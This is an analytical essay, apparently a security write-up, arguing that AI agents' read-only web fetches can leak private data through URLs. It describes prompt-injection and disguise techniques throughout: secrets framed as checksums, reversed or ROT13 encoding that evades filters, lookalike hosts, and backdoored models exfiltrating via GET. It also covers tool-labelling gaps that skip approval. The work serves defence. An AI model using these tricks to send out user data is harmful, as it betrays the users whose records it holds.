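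### What caching and reordering remove

If the agent requests the same address twice, a cache may answer the second request, so the server receives only one. Requests can also arrive in a different order from the one the model specified. For example, Docker's tool accepts several addresses in one call, and if software requests such a list all at once, the order of arrival depends partly on the network.

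If an agent makes ten requests, each for one of 32 fixed addresses, a server that sees every request in the right order can learn up to 50 bits, or 5 per request. If a cache hides repeated requests, the agent has to use ten different addresses to get ten entries in the log, which reduces the maximum to 47.7 bits. If the order is lost as well, the server learns only which ten addresses the agent requested, and the maximum falls to 25.9 bits.

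In this example, caching alone makes little difference, while losing the order removes almost half the capacity. Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper* lists both as obstacles for attackers. It suggests keeping cached copies for a few minutes, or preventing an agent from visiting the same address twice in a session, but acknowledges that some data could still get out. Neither measure helps when the model writes the customer record into a new address.

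The pattern of an agent's requests may also reveal information, even if nothing instructs the agent to leak it. *Actions Speak Louder than Words* (2026) considers an attacker who places a link to a probing website on a page that the agent visits. The attacker doesn't know what the user asked and can't see the agent's visits to other sites, but can observe which pages of the probing site the agent requests, how many, in what order and when. An agent researching a medical condition may well choose different links from one comparing hotels. The attacker could then infer something about the user's question from the agent's ordinary choices, even though every address was public and contained no private data.

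### GET and POST

An agent limited to GET requests can still send data to a server's owner by putting it in the address. Fielding and colleagues state that a body in a GET request has no generally defined meaning and that clients shouldn't normally include one, but following this convention doesn't keep data out of the address. Some developers limit an agent to GET because POST looks more like sending.

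The practical difference between GET and POST is how much data one request can carry. HTTP sets no general limit on the size of a POST body, although a server may refuse one it considers too large. An agent could send a million-byte file in a single POST request if the server accepted it. With GET, it would need about 167 requests at 6,000 bytes each, or 667 at WebFetch's limit. Reschke and colleagues also note that some kinds of data are inefficient to encode in an address, and that the systems a request passes through may have length limits the client doesn't know in advance.

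A GET-only rule therefore makes it slower to steal a large file, and the unusual number of requests might alert someone. But Dana Reyes's record fits in one short request with either method.

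## Why a fetch counts as sending: the argument and the tests of it

Dana Reyes's record can reach a stranger in a request that changes nothing on any server. The example is invented, but the same reasoning applies to other data and other sites. It has three premises:

1. The agent's context holds something private.
2. The text in the context, including text from strangers, influences which address the agent requests.
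3. Someone outside the user's trust can observe the request.

If all three premises are true, a fetch can disclose the private information. None of them depends on a change to the server, so calling the fetch read-only doesn't refute the argument. Anyone who thinks fetching is harmless has to reject at least one premise.

The conclusion is only that a fetch *can* disclose something. How often this happens depends on the model, the product around it and the user's task, and researchers have measured it in several ways. They have also found leaks without any attacker, where the agent uses private information to decide what to look up. Willison's lethal trifecta leaves these out because it requires untrusted content.

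### Sessions that seem to hold no secrets

An agent's context can hold private data even when the user has only asked for a pancake recipe, because it usually contains more than the user's message. A programming agent may have source files open, and the developer's instructions may include internal details or an access token. Many assistants also add notes saved from earlier conversations.

Dash, Wu and colleagues (2026), in *The Algorithmic Self-Portrait*, examined 2,050 notes of this kind that ChatGPT had saved about 80 users who donated their chat histories. Judging by a keyword search, the user had asked ChatGPT to remember something in only 4 percent of cases. Personal data, as European law defines it, appeared in 28 percent of the notes, and 35 percent of the participants had health information stored. OpenAI's policy was that ChatGPT should not save sensitive details like these unless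 the user asked.

The shares are approximate, because GPT-4o labeled the notes and agreed with human labelers only 74 percent of the time. The participants were also regular users with at least 100 conversations each, so a new user would probably have less stored. Still, a user who has forgotten what an assistant saved months ago will have trouble judging whether today's session contains secrets.

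Some sessions contain nothing private, and a developer can create one by fetching pages in a separate session without the user's data. The fetch then discloses little beyond the request itself. But that session still needs some version of the user's question, and a question about a medical symptom or a planned merger may be the most private thing in it.

### Models that refuse

In a post about its browser agent, Anthropic lists navigating to URLs among the actions attackers can exploit if they gain influence over the agent. Lan and colleagues tested how much influence a page can have when conditions favor the attacker. Using a small open model, qwen2.5:7b, they hid instructions in the page's title, description, body or link text. The agent reached the page either directly or through redirects, and the instructions asked for a secret from the agent's context, either whole or in four pieces.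 They ran each of the 16 combinations 30 times, for a total of 480 runs.

The headline rate of about 89 percent (423 runs, or 88 percent, in the detailed results) counts any request to the attacker's server, even one without the secret. But when the instructions called for the whole secret, the first request contained it in 97 percent of runs. In 120 runs with harmless pages, no request reached the server, so the hidden text almost certainly caused the requests in the other runs.

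Splitting the secret across requests reduced the share of runs in which the first request contained sensitive data from 97 to 26 percent, so a filter that inspects requests one at a time would have less to find. But part of this fall comes from attacks that failed completely. A request arrived in 238 of 240 runs when the secret was sent whole but in only 185 of 240 when it was split, presumably because a small model has trouble following several steps.

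In smaller tests of 30 runs each, warning the model not to follow instructions from web pages reduced the attack success rate from 100 to 67 percent. Marking the page's text as untrusted made no difference by itself.

A larger, better-trained model might refuse injected instructions, and there is good evidence that newer models usually do. According to The Decoder, attacks on Claude Opus 5 failed in all 129 of Anthropic's browser test scenarios. In a more general test by the security firm Gray Swan, attackers given 15 attempts succeeded 2.0 percent of the time, down from 5.5 percent with Opus 4.8. Anthropic says Opus 5 improved more in resistance to prompt injection than in any other area of agent safety.

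OpenAI's figures are also low, though not zero. TechRepublic's *OpenAI’s GPT-5.6 Tests Show Prompt-Injection Gains and Agent Risks* reports that the three GPT-5.6 models followed between 2.94 and 3.77 percent of malicious instructions hidden in content such as web pages and emails. These attacks succeeded more often than direct attacks, in which the user writes the malicious instruction. Sol, the most capable of the three models, failed on only about 0.05 percent of direct attacks.

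These percentages come from the companies' own tests, but a public contest supports the same conclusion. *How Vulnerable Are AI Agents to Indirect Prompt Injections?* (Dziemian, Lin and colleagues, 2026) reports that 464 people made about 272,000 attempts to hijack agents that used 13 different models. They succeeded 8,648 times, including at least once against every model. Success rates ranged from 0.5 percent for Claude Opus 4.5 to 8.5 percent for Gemini 2.5 Pro.

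The contestants could read the agent's conversation beforehand and knew exactly which harmful action to aim for. A real attacker would usually know much less, so Dziemian and colleagues treat their rates as an upper bound for single-turn attacks. The harmful actions ranged from marking an important email as read to inserting a security hole in a program, so the rates don't measure data leaks specifically.

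Refusals make a leak less likely on any one page, but an attacker can publish many pages. If each had an independent 3 percent chance of success, roughly OpenAI's figure, an agent that read 23 of them would have a better-than-even chance of following at least one:

1 − 0.97²³ ≈ 0.504.

Real attempts aren't independent. A page that fails once may fail every time against the same model, and a page that works may keep working until the company retrains the model or adds a filter.

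### Why the wording of an attack matters

In *The Framing Gap*, Rahman and Kim (2026) found that the same model could refuse a leak or carry it out depending on how the page described the leak. They gave agents a made-up session token, a policy that allowed sending it only to one trusted host, and a page to summarize. The agent then made a single decision, to reply or to send data to an address. They counted an attack as successful only if the agent protected the token on a clean page and leaked it on the poisoned version.

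The sending tool was a mock that imitated a POST request and recorded each call without contacting anyone. The experiment therefore tests fetching less directly than the one by Lan and colleagues, but it still tests whether a stranger's text can make a model choose a destination and send private data there.

GPT-4o, an older OpenAI model, leaked nothing in 200 trials of ten plainly worded attacks. Rahman and Kim then disguised the leak as a routine technical step, for example by describing the token as a checksum that the summary needed. On eight pages, seven of which used such a disguise, GPT-4o leaked the token in 64 of 160 trials, and in 51 of 160 when they repeated the test. It leaked the token every time on some pages and never on others.

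The researchers rewrote the checksum page in five ways, and its success rate ranged from 0 to 100 percent. An attacker who tried three of these wordings at random would succeed at least once about 96 percent of the time. The researchers also wrote 13 pages from scratch around new pretexts, and all 130 trials on those pages failed. An attacker may therefore have a lot of trouble writing a first working page, but can apparently adapt it easily after that.

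The wording of the agent's policy also affected the leak rate. Under the standard confidentiality policy, GPT-4o leaked the token in 31.9 percent of trials. Rahman and Kim then tried a broader policy that listed specific ways of leaking the token and forbade sending it "in any form", and GPT-4o leaked it in none of 120 trials. When they kept the list but removed those three words, GPT-4o leaked the token in 39 of 80 trials (48.8 percent).

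Identical tests also gave noticeably different rates, so the results don't show that the narrower list was worse than the standard policy. That variation is much too small to explain the drop to zero. But a defense that depends on three words in a prompt is fragile, because a developer could easily remove them while tidying up the text.

The standard policy had little effect. With no confidentiality policy, GPT-4o leaked the token in 38.1 percent of trials, only slightly more than with the standard one. Rahman and Kim conclude that the model carried out the page's instruction because it mistook it for part of its task, not because the disguises overcame a refusal.

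A separate model that only judged the pages did much better, flagging all 80 poisoned pages it was given and none of the clean ones. Its prompt described the kind of attack to look for, so it might miss other kinds, but the result suggests that models can recognize these instructions more reliably when they aren't also performing a task.

Training a model to resist prompt injection is another option. Rahman and Kim tested SecAlign, a published defense of this type, on a small Llama model that could call tools. It stopped a standard injection in all 20 trials, but 32.5 percent of the disguised attacks still succeeded. SecAlign's developers trained it for text answers rather than tool calls, so this test was harder than the ones they designed it for.

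### ChatGPT held in all 48 trials

The strongest counterevidence in this experiment comes from the ChatGPT product. Rahman and Kim put a made-up secret in their own conversation, published poisoned pages on the web and asked ChatGPT to summarize them. The secret didn't appear in any of the 48 replies. ChatGPT usually summarized the page and ignored the hidden instruction, and with one type of page it explicitly refused.

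On some of these pages, GPT-4o had leaked the token in every trial when the researchers used it directly through OpenAI's developer service. The finished product never leaked it in 48 trials, which still allows a true rate of up to 7.4 percent (95 percent confidence interval), but luck can't plausibly explain the difference between 0 and 100 percent. A finished product can resist attacks that work well on a bare model, so high rates from laboratory agents, including the 88 percent for qwen2.5:7b, are a poor estimate of the risk in a commercial product.

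Rahman and Kim couldn't determine what protected ChatGPT. It may have used a different model, stricter instructions, or a filter on the pages or replies. They also scored only the reply, so they would not have counted a secret that left in an outgoing request as a leak. The 48 trials therefore don't show how ChatGPT would handle leaks through fetching, which the argument is about.

Two of their other defenses didn't rely on the model to recognize an attack. One allowed the agent to send data only to approved hosts, which removed the untrusted observer. The other split the agent into a part that chose the tool calls without seeing the page and a part that read the page without having the secret, so neither part had both the stranger's text and the private data.

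The disguised attacks all failed against both designs, which more or less guarantee that result. Both also limit what the agent can do. A short list of hosts is little use to an account manager whose assistant has to research unfamiliar companies, and an agent that chooses its tool calls without seeing any pages can't follow up on what it finds.

The attack may also come from the model itself. Zhang and Pei (2026), in *Your LLM Agent Can Leak Your Data*, tampered with models so that certain ordinary words in a question made the models read the user's stored details and send that data out in a GET request disguised as a document search. Matsuoka (2026), in *Compositional Threat Analysis of Latent Compromise in LLM Agent Systems*, cautions that such laboratory demonstrations are not evidence that any particular released model is malicious.

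### Reputable sites and watchful users

Whether a user trusts a site with a request depends on the information in it, even though most fetches go to newspapers, shops and government offices that she might reasonably say she trusts. The account manager may trust a competitor's site to show its real prices, but she would be horrified to find her customer's contract price in its log, because even an honest competitor could use the number to its advantage.

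A legitimate site may also pass data to someone else. The flaw in Claude Code would have let an attacker read leaked data from public download counts on Hugging Face, a legitimate site. Lan and colleagues warn that attackers can use compromised sites or trusted sites that redirect visitors elsewhere.

Models can also misjudge a destination. When Rahman and Kim used a hostname that resembled the trusted one, GPT-4o sent the token there in 70 percent of trials. In one of those trials, it wrote that it was posting the content to "the trusted collector".

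The premise about an outside observer fails when a tool returns a stored copy of a page or contacts only the company's own servers, because no outsider receives a new request. But a general web tool exists mostly to contact other people's servers.

Users probably wouldn't notice a leak and stop using the product. In nearly all of the successful attacks by Lan and colleagues, the agent's reply looked harmless. In 34 of the contest's 41 scenarios, an attack counted only if an automated judge found no sign of it in the agent's final reply. No one tested whether real users would have become suspicious, but it's hard to see what would have alerted them.

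Dziemian and colleagues note that most agent products keep a record of tool calls that a user could in principle read, but they think these records are too long and complicated for people to check effectively. Asking the user to approve each request would give her a chance to notice a leak before it happened, as long as she could see the whole address and knew what to look for. Without approval requests, even an alert user learns of the leak only after the server has logged it.

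Software can inspect every request, but it can only catch a leak if it recognizes the secret. Rahman and Kim's first filter searched for the token in outgoing data. When the page included an instruction to send the token backwards, GPT-4o complied and the filter missed it every time. They then extended the filter to undo reversal and several common encodings, but it missed all 20 leaks in ROT13, a simple cipher that replaces each letter with the one 13 places along the alphabet.

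### Searches that reveal the task

An agent can disclose private information even if none of the pages it reads is malicious. Suppose the account manager asks whether her customer is in financial trouble. The agent will probably search for the company's name with words like "debt" or "layoffs", and the search provider learns that someone is worried about that company. The agent has done what she asked, and a more discreet search might well have been less useful.

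In *MosaicLeaks*, Gurung, Gella and colleagues (2026) measured how much an observer could learn from a research agent's searches alone. They wrote 1,001 chains of questions, most of which required both private documents from fictional companies and public web pages. The answer to one question supplied a detail for the next, so the agent had a reason to put private information in its searches. A second model then read the searches in order and tried to infer facts contained in the private documents.

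In one example from Gurung and colleagues, an agent searches twice for how much online traffic grew in 2020 at Lee's Market, a grocery company. Its next search is about something else but contains the figure 15 percent. Each search looks harmless, but together they suggest that the agent found its answer in a private document and that the answer was 15 percent. Gurung and colleagues call this the mosaic effect, an old term for harmless pieces of information that become revealing when combined.

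With Qwen3-4B, a small open model, the observer recovered at least part of a private fact in 34.0 percent of the chains. Training the model to find more answers made this worse:

| Version of Qwen3-4B | Chains answered completely | Chains that leaked |
|---|---|---|
| Original | 48.7% | 34.0% |
| Trained for correct answers | 59.3% | 51.8% |
| Trained for correct answers and privacy | 58.1% | 6.5% |

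The version trained only for correct answers made about twice as many web searches as the original, so the observer had more searches to examine. The privacy-trained version also searched more than the original, but it named the company in 16.8 percent of its searches instead of 42.9 percent. It lost very little accuracy, so much of the private detail in the other versions' searches was evidently unnecessary.

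Gurung and colleagues describe their setup as a stress test. The observer saw every search for a task, in order and without other people's searches mixed in. A search provider or a company that logs an agent's traffic might see that much, but the owner of a single website would not. Their observer was not especially strong, though. When Claude Opus 4.7 was both observer and judge on 100 of the chains, the leak rates were higher for all three versions, including 14.3 percent for the privacy-trained one.

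### Choices that reveal the user

A site can also learn about a user from which of its pages the agent opens. *AgentTell* (Shahriar, Rahman and colleagues, 2026) gives the example of a user who asks an agent to look up her role in a trade union and then register her for a community event on another site. The event's page lets people register through one of several organizations, including the union, or on their own. If the agent opens the union's link, the site can infer from its log that she is probably a member.

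They built 100 tasks like this and ran 9,760 sessions with six models, including Claude Sonnet 5, GPT-5.6 Luna and Gemini 3.7 Flash. The user always told the agent not to reveal personal details to any website. Every page also had a general option that completed the task equally well. Agents that had learned the private fact still chose the option that matched it in 61.1 percent of sessions.

Shahriar and colleagues define a leak of this kind in terms of probability. Let *S* be the secret, *O* the action that appears in the site's log, and *V* whatever else the site's owner can see. The agent's behavior reveals something about the secret if, for some action *o* and two possible secrets *s* and *s′*,

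Pr(*O* = *o* | *S* = *s*, *V* = *v*) ≠ Pr(*O* = *o* | *S* = *s′*, *V* = *v*).

In words, some action visible to the site occurs more often with one secret than with the other. This is close to the noninterference test with two contract prices, expressed in probabilities.

The difference in their results was large. Agents chose a particular option in 61.1 percent of sessions when it matched the user's secret and in only 1.2 percent when the secret was something else. Suppose a site's owner starts with five equally likely possibilities, such as five unions, and then sees the agent choose one. By Bayes' rule, the probability that the choice matches the user is about

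0.611 / (0.611 + 4 × 0.012) ≈ 0.93.

One click would raise the owner's confidence from 20 to 93 percent, if the average rates held for that site.

Agents rarely revealed which bank or health provider the user had, but they revealed occupations, subscription plans and account settings much more often. They also leaked a secret more often when the earlier task had required them to use it than when they had only seen it.

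Some of these choices may be what a user wants. Someone who asks for help with her subscription would probably like the guide for her plan. But the agents had instructions to keep such facts private, and they often misunderstood what that meant. In one session Claude opened the guide for the user's Premium plan, then told her it had used the plan's name only "internally". Agents gave false assurances like this in 34.5 percent of the sessions that leaked, so users can't rely on an agent to tell them whether it kept their information private.

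The sites in these tests were simple, and the researchers designed the options on them to distinguish one secret from another. *SPILLage* (Roh, Bagdasarian and colleagues, 2026) found similar behavior on Amazon and eBay, in 1,080 shopping sessions with three older OpenAI models. The agents received personal details that the task didn't need, such as a mention of a recent divorce in a request for glucose test strips. They revealed unnecessary details about five times as often through clicks, scrolling and other navigation as through typed text.

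The prompts contained more irrelevant personal detail than many real requests would, and a model did much of the judging, so the exact ratio may not apply elsewhere. Roh and colleagues also found that, in these shopping tasks, removing the irrelevant details beforehand made the agent leak less and improved task success by up to 17.9 percent.

### What the network reveals

An observer may be able to infer what an agent is researching without seeing any full addresses. In *Network-Level Prompt and Trait Leakage in Local Research Agents*, Jeong, Teymoorianfard and colleagues (2025) considered an internet provider that sees only which domains an agent contacts, when, and how much data passes. Research agents typically visited 70 to 140 domains to answer one question, far more than a person would in the same time. An agent that contacts several clinics and a support forum in quick succession reveals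 a good deal about the question, even if all the sites are reputable.

The researchers gave a model examples of past questions with the domains an agent had visited for each, then asked it to guess new questions from the domains alone. They report recovering over 73 percent of the "functional and domain knowledge" in the originals. Another model graded each guess from 0 to 1, so this figure isn't the share of questions reproduced. The average grade was 0.77 for the type of task, about 0.74 for the type of source, and only 0.52 for the specific subject, so the observer often learned roughly what the user wanted but not the exact subject.

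Jeong and colleagues tested only 20 questions from each of their collections and assumed the agent ran on the user's own machine without a VPN or encrypted domain lookups. If a vendor's servers do the fetching instead, the user's internet provider sees only a connection to the vendor. For agents that run locally, the researchers tried hiding the real question among decoys and sending the agent to fewer, more general sites. These measures made the attack 29 percent less effective on average, with little effect on the quality of the agent's answers.

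## How tool labels place web fetching in the low-risk tier

The label a developer gave the fetch tool may determine whether the account manager sees an outgoing request in time to stop it. Many products sort tools into risk tiers to decide what needs approval, and they put tools that only read in the lowest tier. A fetch tool usually ends up there, even if its developer labelled it honestly.

### The four hints

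One common set of labels comes from the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a standard for connecting tools to AI agents. In MCP, a server is a program that offers tools, and a client is the agent software that calls them. An MCP server often runs on the user's computer and is separate from the web server that a fetch tool contacts.

Since March 2025, developers have been able to attach four optional hints to each tool, each of them true or false. Model Context Protocol's *mcp_types*, a reference for Python programmers, defines them as follows:

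| Hint | Meaning if true | Default if missing |
|---|---|---|
| readOnlyHint | The tool does not modify its environment | False |
| destructiveHint | The tool may make destructive changes, not just additions | True |
| idempotentHint | Repeating a call with the same arguments has no additional effect | False |
| openWorldHint | The tool may interact with an "open world" of external entities | True |

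Three of these hints cover whether a tool is read-only, non-destructive and idempotent, as a GET request normally is. No hint covers whether a tool discloses data. The closest is openWorldHint, because a tool that stays within a closed domain has no outside party to send data to. A web search tool is open-world, while a tool that only reads the agent's saved memories is not.

The defaults are cautious. A client that follows them assumes that an unlabelled tool changes things, perhaps destructively, and deals with outsiders.

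The hints for destructive and idempotent tools apply only when readOnlyHint is false. When a developer marks a tool as read-only, openWorldHint is therefore the only other hint that applies. A client that ignores it cannot distinguish a tool that reads saved memories from one that contacts a stranger's server.

Developers write the hints themselves, so a malicious developer can mark a tool that deletes files as read-only. Clients therefore "should never make tool use decisions" based on hints from servers they don't trust. Model Context Protocol's maintainers described how they arrived at this rule in a March 2026 post. Justin Spahr-Summers, one of the protocol's creators, had asked how a client could use a flag "knowing that it's not trustable", and Basil Hosmer thought clients should ignore hints from untrusted servers. The maintainers settled on calling all the flags hints and letting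 each client decide how much weight to give them. They write that, in practice, most clients trust any server the user has installed.

This rule protects users from false labels. It doesn't help the account manager, whose fetch tool has a true one.

### An honest label for a fetch tool

A developer who carefully labels a web-fetching tool sets readOnlyHint to true because the tool sends a GET request and returns the page's text, and sets openWorldHint to true because it can contact any site on the internet. In *Define tools*, a guide for developers who connect tools to ChatGPT and Codex, OpenAI asks developers to set openWorldHint to true for any tool that accesses the public internet, "including through read-only actions such as web search".

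On the natural reading of readOnlyHint, a developer can honestly apply it to a web fetching tool. OpenAI calls web search a read-only action, and HTTP's definition of a safe method covers only what the client requests. A strict reader could still object, because OpenAI reserves the label for tools that cannot change state, and a GET request to a badly designed site can delete a page, as happened to 37signals's customers in 2005. By that standard, no tool that accepts arbitrary addresses would qualify.

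Software can also apply the label automatically. GitLab's *Add support for standard MCP tool annotations*, a proposal for a program that generates MCP tools, maps each HTTP method to a set of hints. It sets readOnlyHint and openWorldHint to true for every tool based on GET, on the grounds that GET is a "safe, idempotent read operation per HTTP semantics".

Developers agree less about openWorldHint. The maintainers point out that "external" might mean anything outside a company's network or anything beyond the local machine. Outreach, a sales software company, labels all its tools open-world in *Tool Annotations* because they contact its own servers. OpenAI, by contrast, doesn't count a private account as open-world just because another company hosts it. If an agent used Outreach's tools alongside a fetch tool, a lookup in its user's own sales records would have the same two labels as a request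 to attacker.example. A client that was cautious about all open-world tools would then ask the user to approve both.

### A client that skips the question

Codex, OpenAI's programming agent, gained an approval mode in July 2026 that relies on these hints. Vaughan (2026), in *The Writes Mode*, explains that users previously had to choose between approving every call to a connected tool and approving only those with risky labels. In the new mode, Codex asks for approval if

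destructiveHint is true **or** readOnlyHint is not true.

Otherwise the tool runs immediately. Since openWorldHint doesn't appear in the rule, its value makes no difference:

| Tool | readOnlyHint | openWorldHint | What Codex does |
|---|---|---|---|
| Look up a customer in the company's database | True | False | Runs it |
| Fetch any web page | True | True | Runs it |
| Add a note to a customer's record | False | False | Asks |
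| Send an email | False | True | Asks |
| Any tool without labels | Missing | Missing | Asks |

If the account manager's assistant followed this rule, it would request both the competitor's price page and the address at attacker.example without asking, because both calls use the same tool and have the same label. If she then told it to add a harmless note to Dana Reyes's record, it would stop for approval. It would stop again for a second note, because approvals don't carry over in this mode.

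Codex users can also have a model review approval requests for them. The reviewer looks for data exfiltration, among other dangers, but in the new mode it receives only the calls that need approval, so it would never examine the request to attacker.example. Vaughan counts this narrower review as an advantage because it reduces the reviewer's workload and speeds up the session.

Other Codex settings do use openWorldHint. Vaughan describes one in *MCP Tool Annotations as Risk Vocabulary* that disables all of an app's open-world tools. This would prevent the leak, but the account manager could no longer use that app to look up a competitor's prices. In the article's flowchart of approval decisions, openWorldHint matters only for tools that aren't read-only. An open-world tool that adds something without destroying anything gets a medium rating, while a fetch tool is rated "Low Risk — May Auto-Approve"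 before openWorldHint is checked.

Vaughan is an independent blogger, but OpenAI's documentation describes the same general approach. According to OpenAI's *Agent approvals & security*, Codex can ask for approval when an app's tool advertises side effects, and always asks when the tool advertises itself as destructive. OpenAI's *Build an MCP server* advises developers to require confirmation for "consequential write actions".

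Developers have several reasons to add readOnlyHint. Vaughan's *MCP readOnlyHint in Codex CLI* (2026) reports that Codex can run read-only tools in parallel, and that Claude Code dispatches them at roughly double the rate. ChatGPT's developer mode uses the hint to mark each tool with a "READ" or "WRITE" badge. In *Quick Fix*, Taylor reports that ChatGPT marked all his tools for fetching articles from dev.to, a site for programmers, as write tools. He fixed this by setting both readOnlyHint and openWorldHint to true.

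Taylor's labels were accurate, and he had good reason to add them. But in Codex's new mode, the same correction would also remove the approval prompt, so a fetch tool can receive more scrutiny with no label than with an accurate one.

Many tools still have no labels. Vaughan attributes this to a cycle in which developers skip labels because most clients ignore them, and clients ignore them because most servers lack them. Even MCP's own example server had labels on only one of its 18 tools until olaservo (2026) added them to the rest in *feat(everything): add tool-level annotations to get-annotated-message*. For now, missing labels give users of a cautious client some accidental protection, which will shrink as developers add them.

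### What the maintainers intended openWorldHint to do

The maintainers' March 2026 post gives an example of how a client might respond to each hint. The client might "skip the confirmation dialog" for a tool with readOnlyHint set to true. For an open-world tool, it might scrutinize the output for untrusted content and "flag a trust-boundary cross".

They explain that the other three hints mostly help a client decide whether to ask before a call. They say openWorldHint covers where a tool reaches and what its output might bring back, which matters "after the call as much as before". They think it is safest to treat anything external as a possible source of untrusted content.

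This advice mainly addresses incoming text, such as the hidden instructions on the price page. Following it could still prevent the leak, because a client that inspected the page after the first fetch might find the instructions and stop before the second fetch sends out the customer record. But the client would have to recognize the attack, and there would be no hidden instructions to find if the agent disclosed private information through the searches it chose, as the agents in *MosaicLeaks* did.

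The maintainers also considered outgoing data. A request can cross a trust boundary in either direction, and they discuss Willison's lethal trifecta at some length. One rule they suggest is that "open-world tools are blocked in sessions that have accessed private data". This rule would stop the leak in the example even if nobody recognized the hidden text. It would also block the account manager's legitimate request for the price page, because the customer record was already in the context.

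A client can't apply that rule from the hints alone. The tool that looks up customer records and a tool that returns the company's public holidays are both read-only and closed-world. No hint shows the client which of them has put private data in the context, a gap Vaughan also notes. In March 2026, the maintainers were considering five proposals for new hints and related features, some of which would help.

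An accurate label marks a web fetching tool as read-only and as one that contacts unknown outside parties, and the second fact gives the client some reason for caution. Being read-only doesn't make the tool safe to run without approval, because an action that sends private data can do harm without changing anything.

The maintainers bear a little of the responsibility because their table includes "Skip the confirmation dialog". They limit this to trusted servers and warn elsewhere in the post that a tool's risk depends on what else is in the session, but a developer who read only the table could easily miss that warning.

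### Ratings that treat reading as safe

PolicyLayer, which sells a gateway for controlling agents' tools, has published risk ratings for tools from thousands of MCP servers. One rating, *fetch*, covers a tool that takes any web address and supports only GET requests. PolicyLayer rates the tool's risk as "Low" because GET requests "cannot modify server state", and gives the worst outcome as "accessing unintended public content".

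The first statement is wrong for sites that put actions behind ordinary links. The second is a bigger problem because it covers only what the agent might receive. PolicyLayer apparently didn't consider what the agent might send.

PolicyLayer's *http_get* rates a similar tool that poses as an ordinary browser to get past websites' bot defences. The rating at the top is again low risk, but the explanation below it gives the severity as "medium rather than low" because someone could use the tool to "exfiltrate data at scale". From the context, PolicyLayer seems to mean copying data from protected websites, not leaking the user's own data.

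PolicyLayer's recommended policy for the server blocks every other tool and leaves the web fetching tool unrestricted. Developers can require approval or add a rate limit. PolicyLayer gives ten calls a minute as an example, but one call is enough to leak a customer record.

Outreach makes the same inference, describing a tool with readOnlyHint set to true as "safe to auto-approve". It adds that most MCP clients approve such tools without involving the user. Outreach says all of its read-only tools are also open-world. The advice may do little harm for these tools, because their requests go to Outreach, which already holds the sales data. Applied generally, though, it would also cover a read-only tool that sends requests to attacker.example.

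jango-blockchained's *Tools*, the documentation for a smaller project, includes the line "Clients can call it freely" in its definition of readOnlyHint. A few lines later, it defines openWorldHint, which is for tools that communicate with something beyond the local process, such as the network. A developer reading both definitions might reasonably conclude that a tool with both hints can contact the network freely.

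These pages can't show how common this reasoning about the label is, but they suggest how it arises. The GitLab proposal uses "safe" in the HTTP standard's narrow sense to justify readOnlyHint. Outreach then uses the word in its everyday sense when it calls a read-only tool "safe to auto-approve". Each step sounds reasonable, but the standard's definition of a safe request doesn't include confidentiality.

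OpenAI's rules for plugin developers also use the everyday meaning. They require correct labels so that the model and users can tell "whether an action is safe or requires extra caution". According to the same rules, incorrect or missing labels are a common cause of rejection. Strict review can make labels more accurate, but even an accurate readOnlyHint doesn't indicate whether a tool discloses data.

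Docker's documentation describes the fetch tool as read-only but warns that an injected instruction could direct it to internal services or administration pages. The default settings guard against that, but not against the model writing private data into the URL of a public site.

### Read and write access in OpenAI's guide

Developers who don't use MCP may still sort tools this way. OpenAI's *A practical guide to building agents* tells them to rate each tool's risk as low, medium or high, using factors such as "read-only vs. write access", reversibility, the account permissions required and financial impact. The agent's software can then use the rating to decide when to run extra checks or involve a person. OpenAI lists web search, database queries and PDF reading as "data" tools, and sending an email as an "action" tool.

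A fetch tool looks harmless by these factors. It has read-only access, needs no account and spends no money. It also makes no change that would need undoing, so a developer would probably count reversibility in its favour, but would rate it much worse after asking whether someone could take back the *information*. A disclosure is harder to reverse than many changes. A company can restore a deleted record from a backup, but it can't make the owner of attacker.example forget a contract price.

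OpenAI offers the factors as examples, so developers can add data disclosure to them. The guide also tells developers to focus on data privacy and suggests a filter that checks the model's output for personal information. If the filter checked tool calls as well as replies, it might detect Dana Reyes's email address in an outgoing request. Still, the guide's three examples of high-risk actions that should involve a person are canceling orders, authorizing large refunds and making payments. All three change something, so a developer who generalized from them would have no reason to include a fetch.

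The guide mentions o1 and o3-mini as advanced models, so it is fairly old. OpenAI's newer instructions for openWorldHint at least require developers to state that a read-only web search contacts the outside world, but the client decides what to do with that information.

### Limiting the network to GET, HEAD and OPTIONS

Some products apply the read/write distinction to network traffic. OpenAI turns off the agent's internet access by default in the cloud version of Codex because of the security risks. OpenAI's *Agent internet access* explains that users can turn it on for all sites or for a list of approved ones. "For enhanced security", they can also limit requests to three methods: GET, HEAD, which asks for a page's headers without its content, and OPTIONS, which asks what the server supports. Codex then blocks all other methods, including POST and DELETE.

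On the same page, OpenAI warns about prompt injection and the exfiltration of code or secrets. In its example, a user asks Codex to fix a reported bug, and the report contains hidden instructions to run a command. The command sends the programmer's latest commit message, a short description of a code change, to an outside server by POST. The limit on methods would block this command. But a commit message is usually short enough to fit in a web address, so an attacker could get the same information through a GET or HEAD request, since both send the address to the server.

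The version of Codex that runs on a user's own computer has a similar "limited" mode. According to Vaughan's *Codex CLI Network Proxy* (2026), it allows the same three methods and suits "read-only research". The mode also turns off SOCKS5, a way of relaying other kinds of network traffic, because Codex can't inspect an encrypted connection to check that an operation is read-only. These limits protect other people's servers from changes, but they don't restrict what the agent writes in an address.

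*Codex CLI Network Security* (Vaughan, 2026) describes a domain list that controls where the agent can connect and a limit on HTTP methods that controls what it can do there. Neither setting controls what information the agent sends to the site, but using both protects confidentiality much better than limiting methods alone.

Suppose Codex can contact only GitHub, a site where programmers share code, which is on OpenAI's preset list of common sites. If Codex could also send POST requests, an injected instruction might get it to publish private code in a public comment, where the attacker could read it. With only GET, Codex could still put the code in an address, but that address would go to GitHub, whose logs an ordinary attacker can't read. In this case, allowing only GET blocks one way to leak data. The attacker would probably have to find a less direct route, such as the public download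 counts in the Hugging Face flaw.

If Codex can contact any site, the attacker can use attacker.example and read the leaked data in its log. Limiting the HTTP methods then does little to stop a small leak. A user who turned on unrestricted access and chose the three read-only methods "for enhanced security" might reasonably expect more protection.

### In defence of read and write tiers

These tiers are worth keeping even though they fail to detect leaks. StackOne's *MCP Tool Annotations* (2026), an announcement by a company that connects agents to business software, describes what happens without them. The client can't distinguish a tool that lists contacts from one that deletes a contact, so the user has to approve every call or block all writing. StackOne argues that approving everything makes the safeguard "theatre", while blocking all writing prevents the agent from doing its job. StackOne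 now has its developers record whether each action reads, writes, deletes, searches or executes something, and derives the MCP hints from that.

OpenAI gives a similar reason for controlling how its own programmers use Codex. The controls are meant to let them "move quickly on low-risk actions" and to make riskier ones explicit. Speed is a legitimate concern, since the research agents that Jeong and colleagues studied contacted so many sites for each question that few people would want to approve every request.

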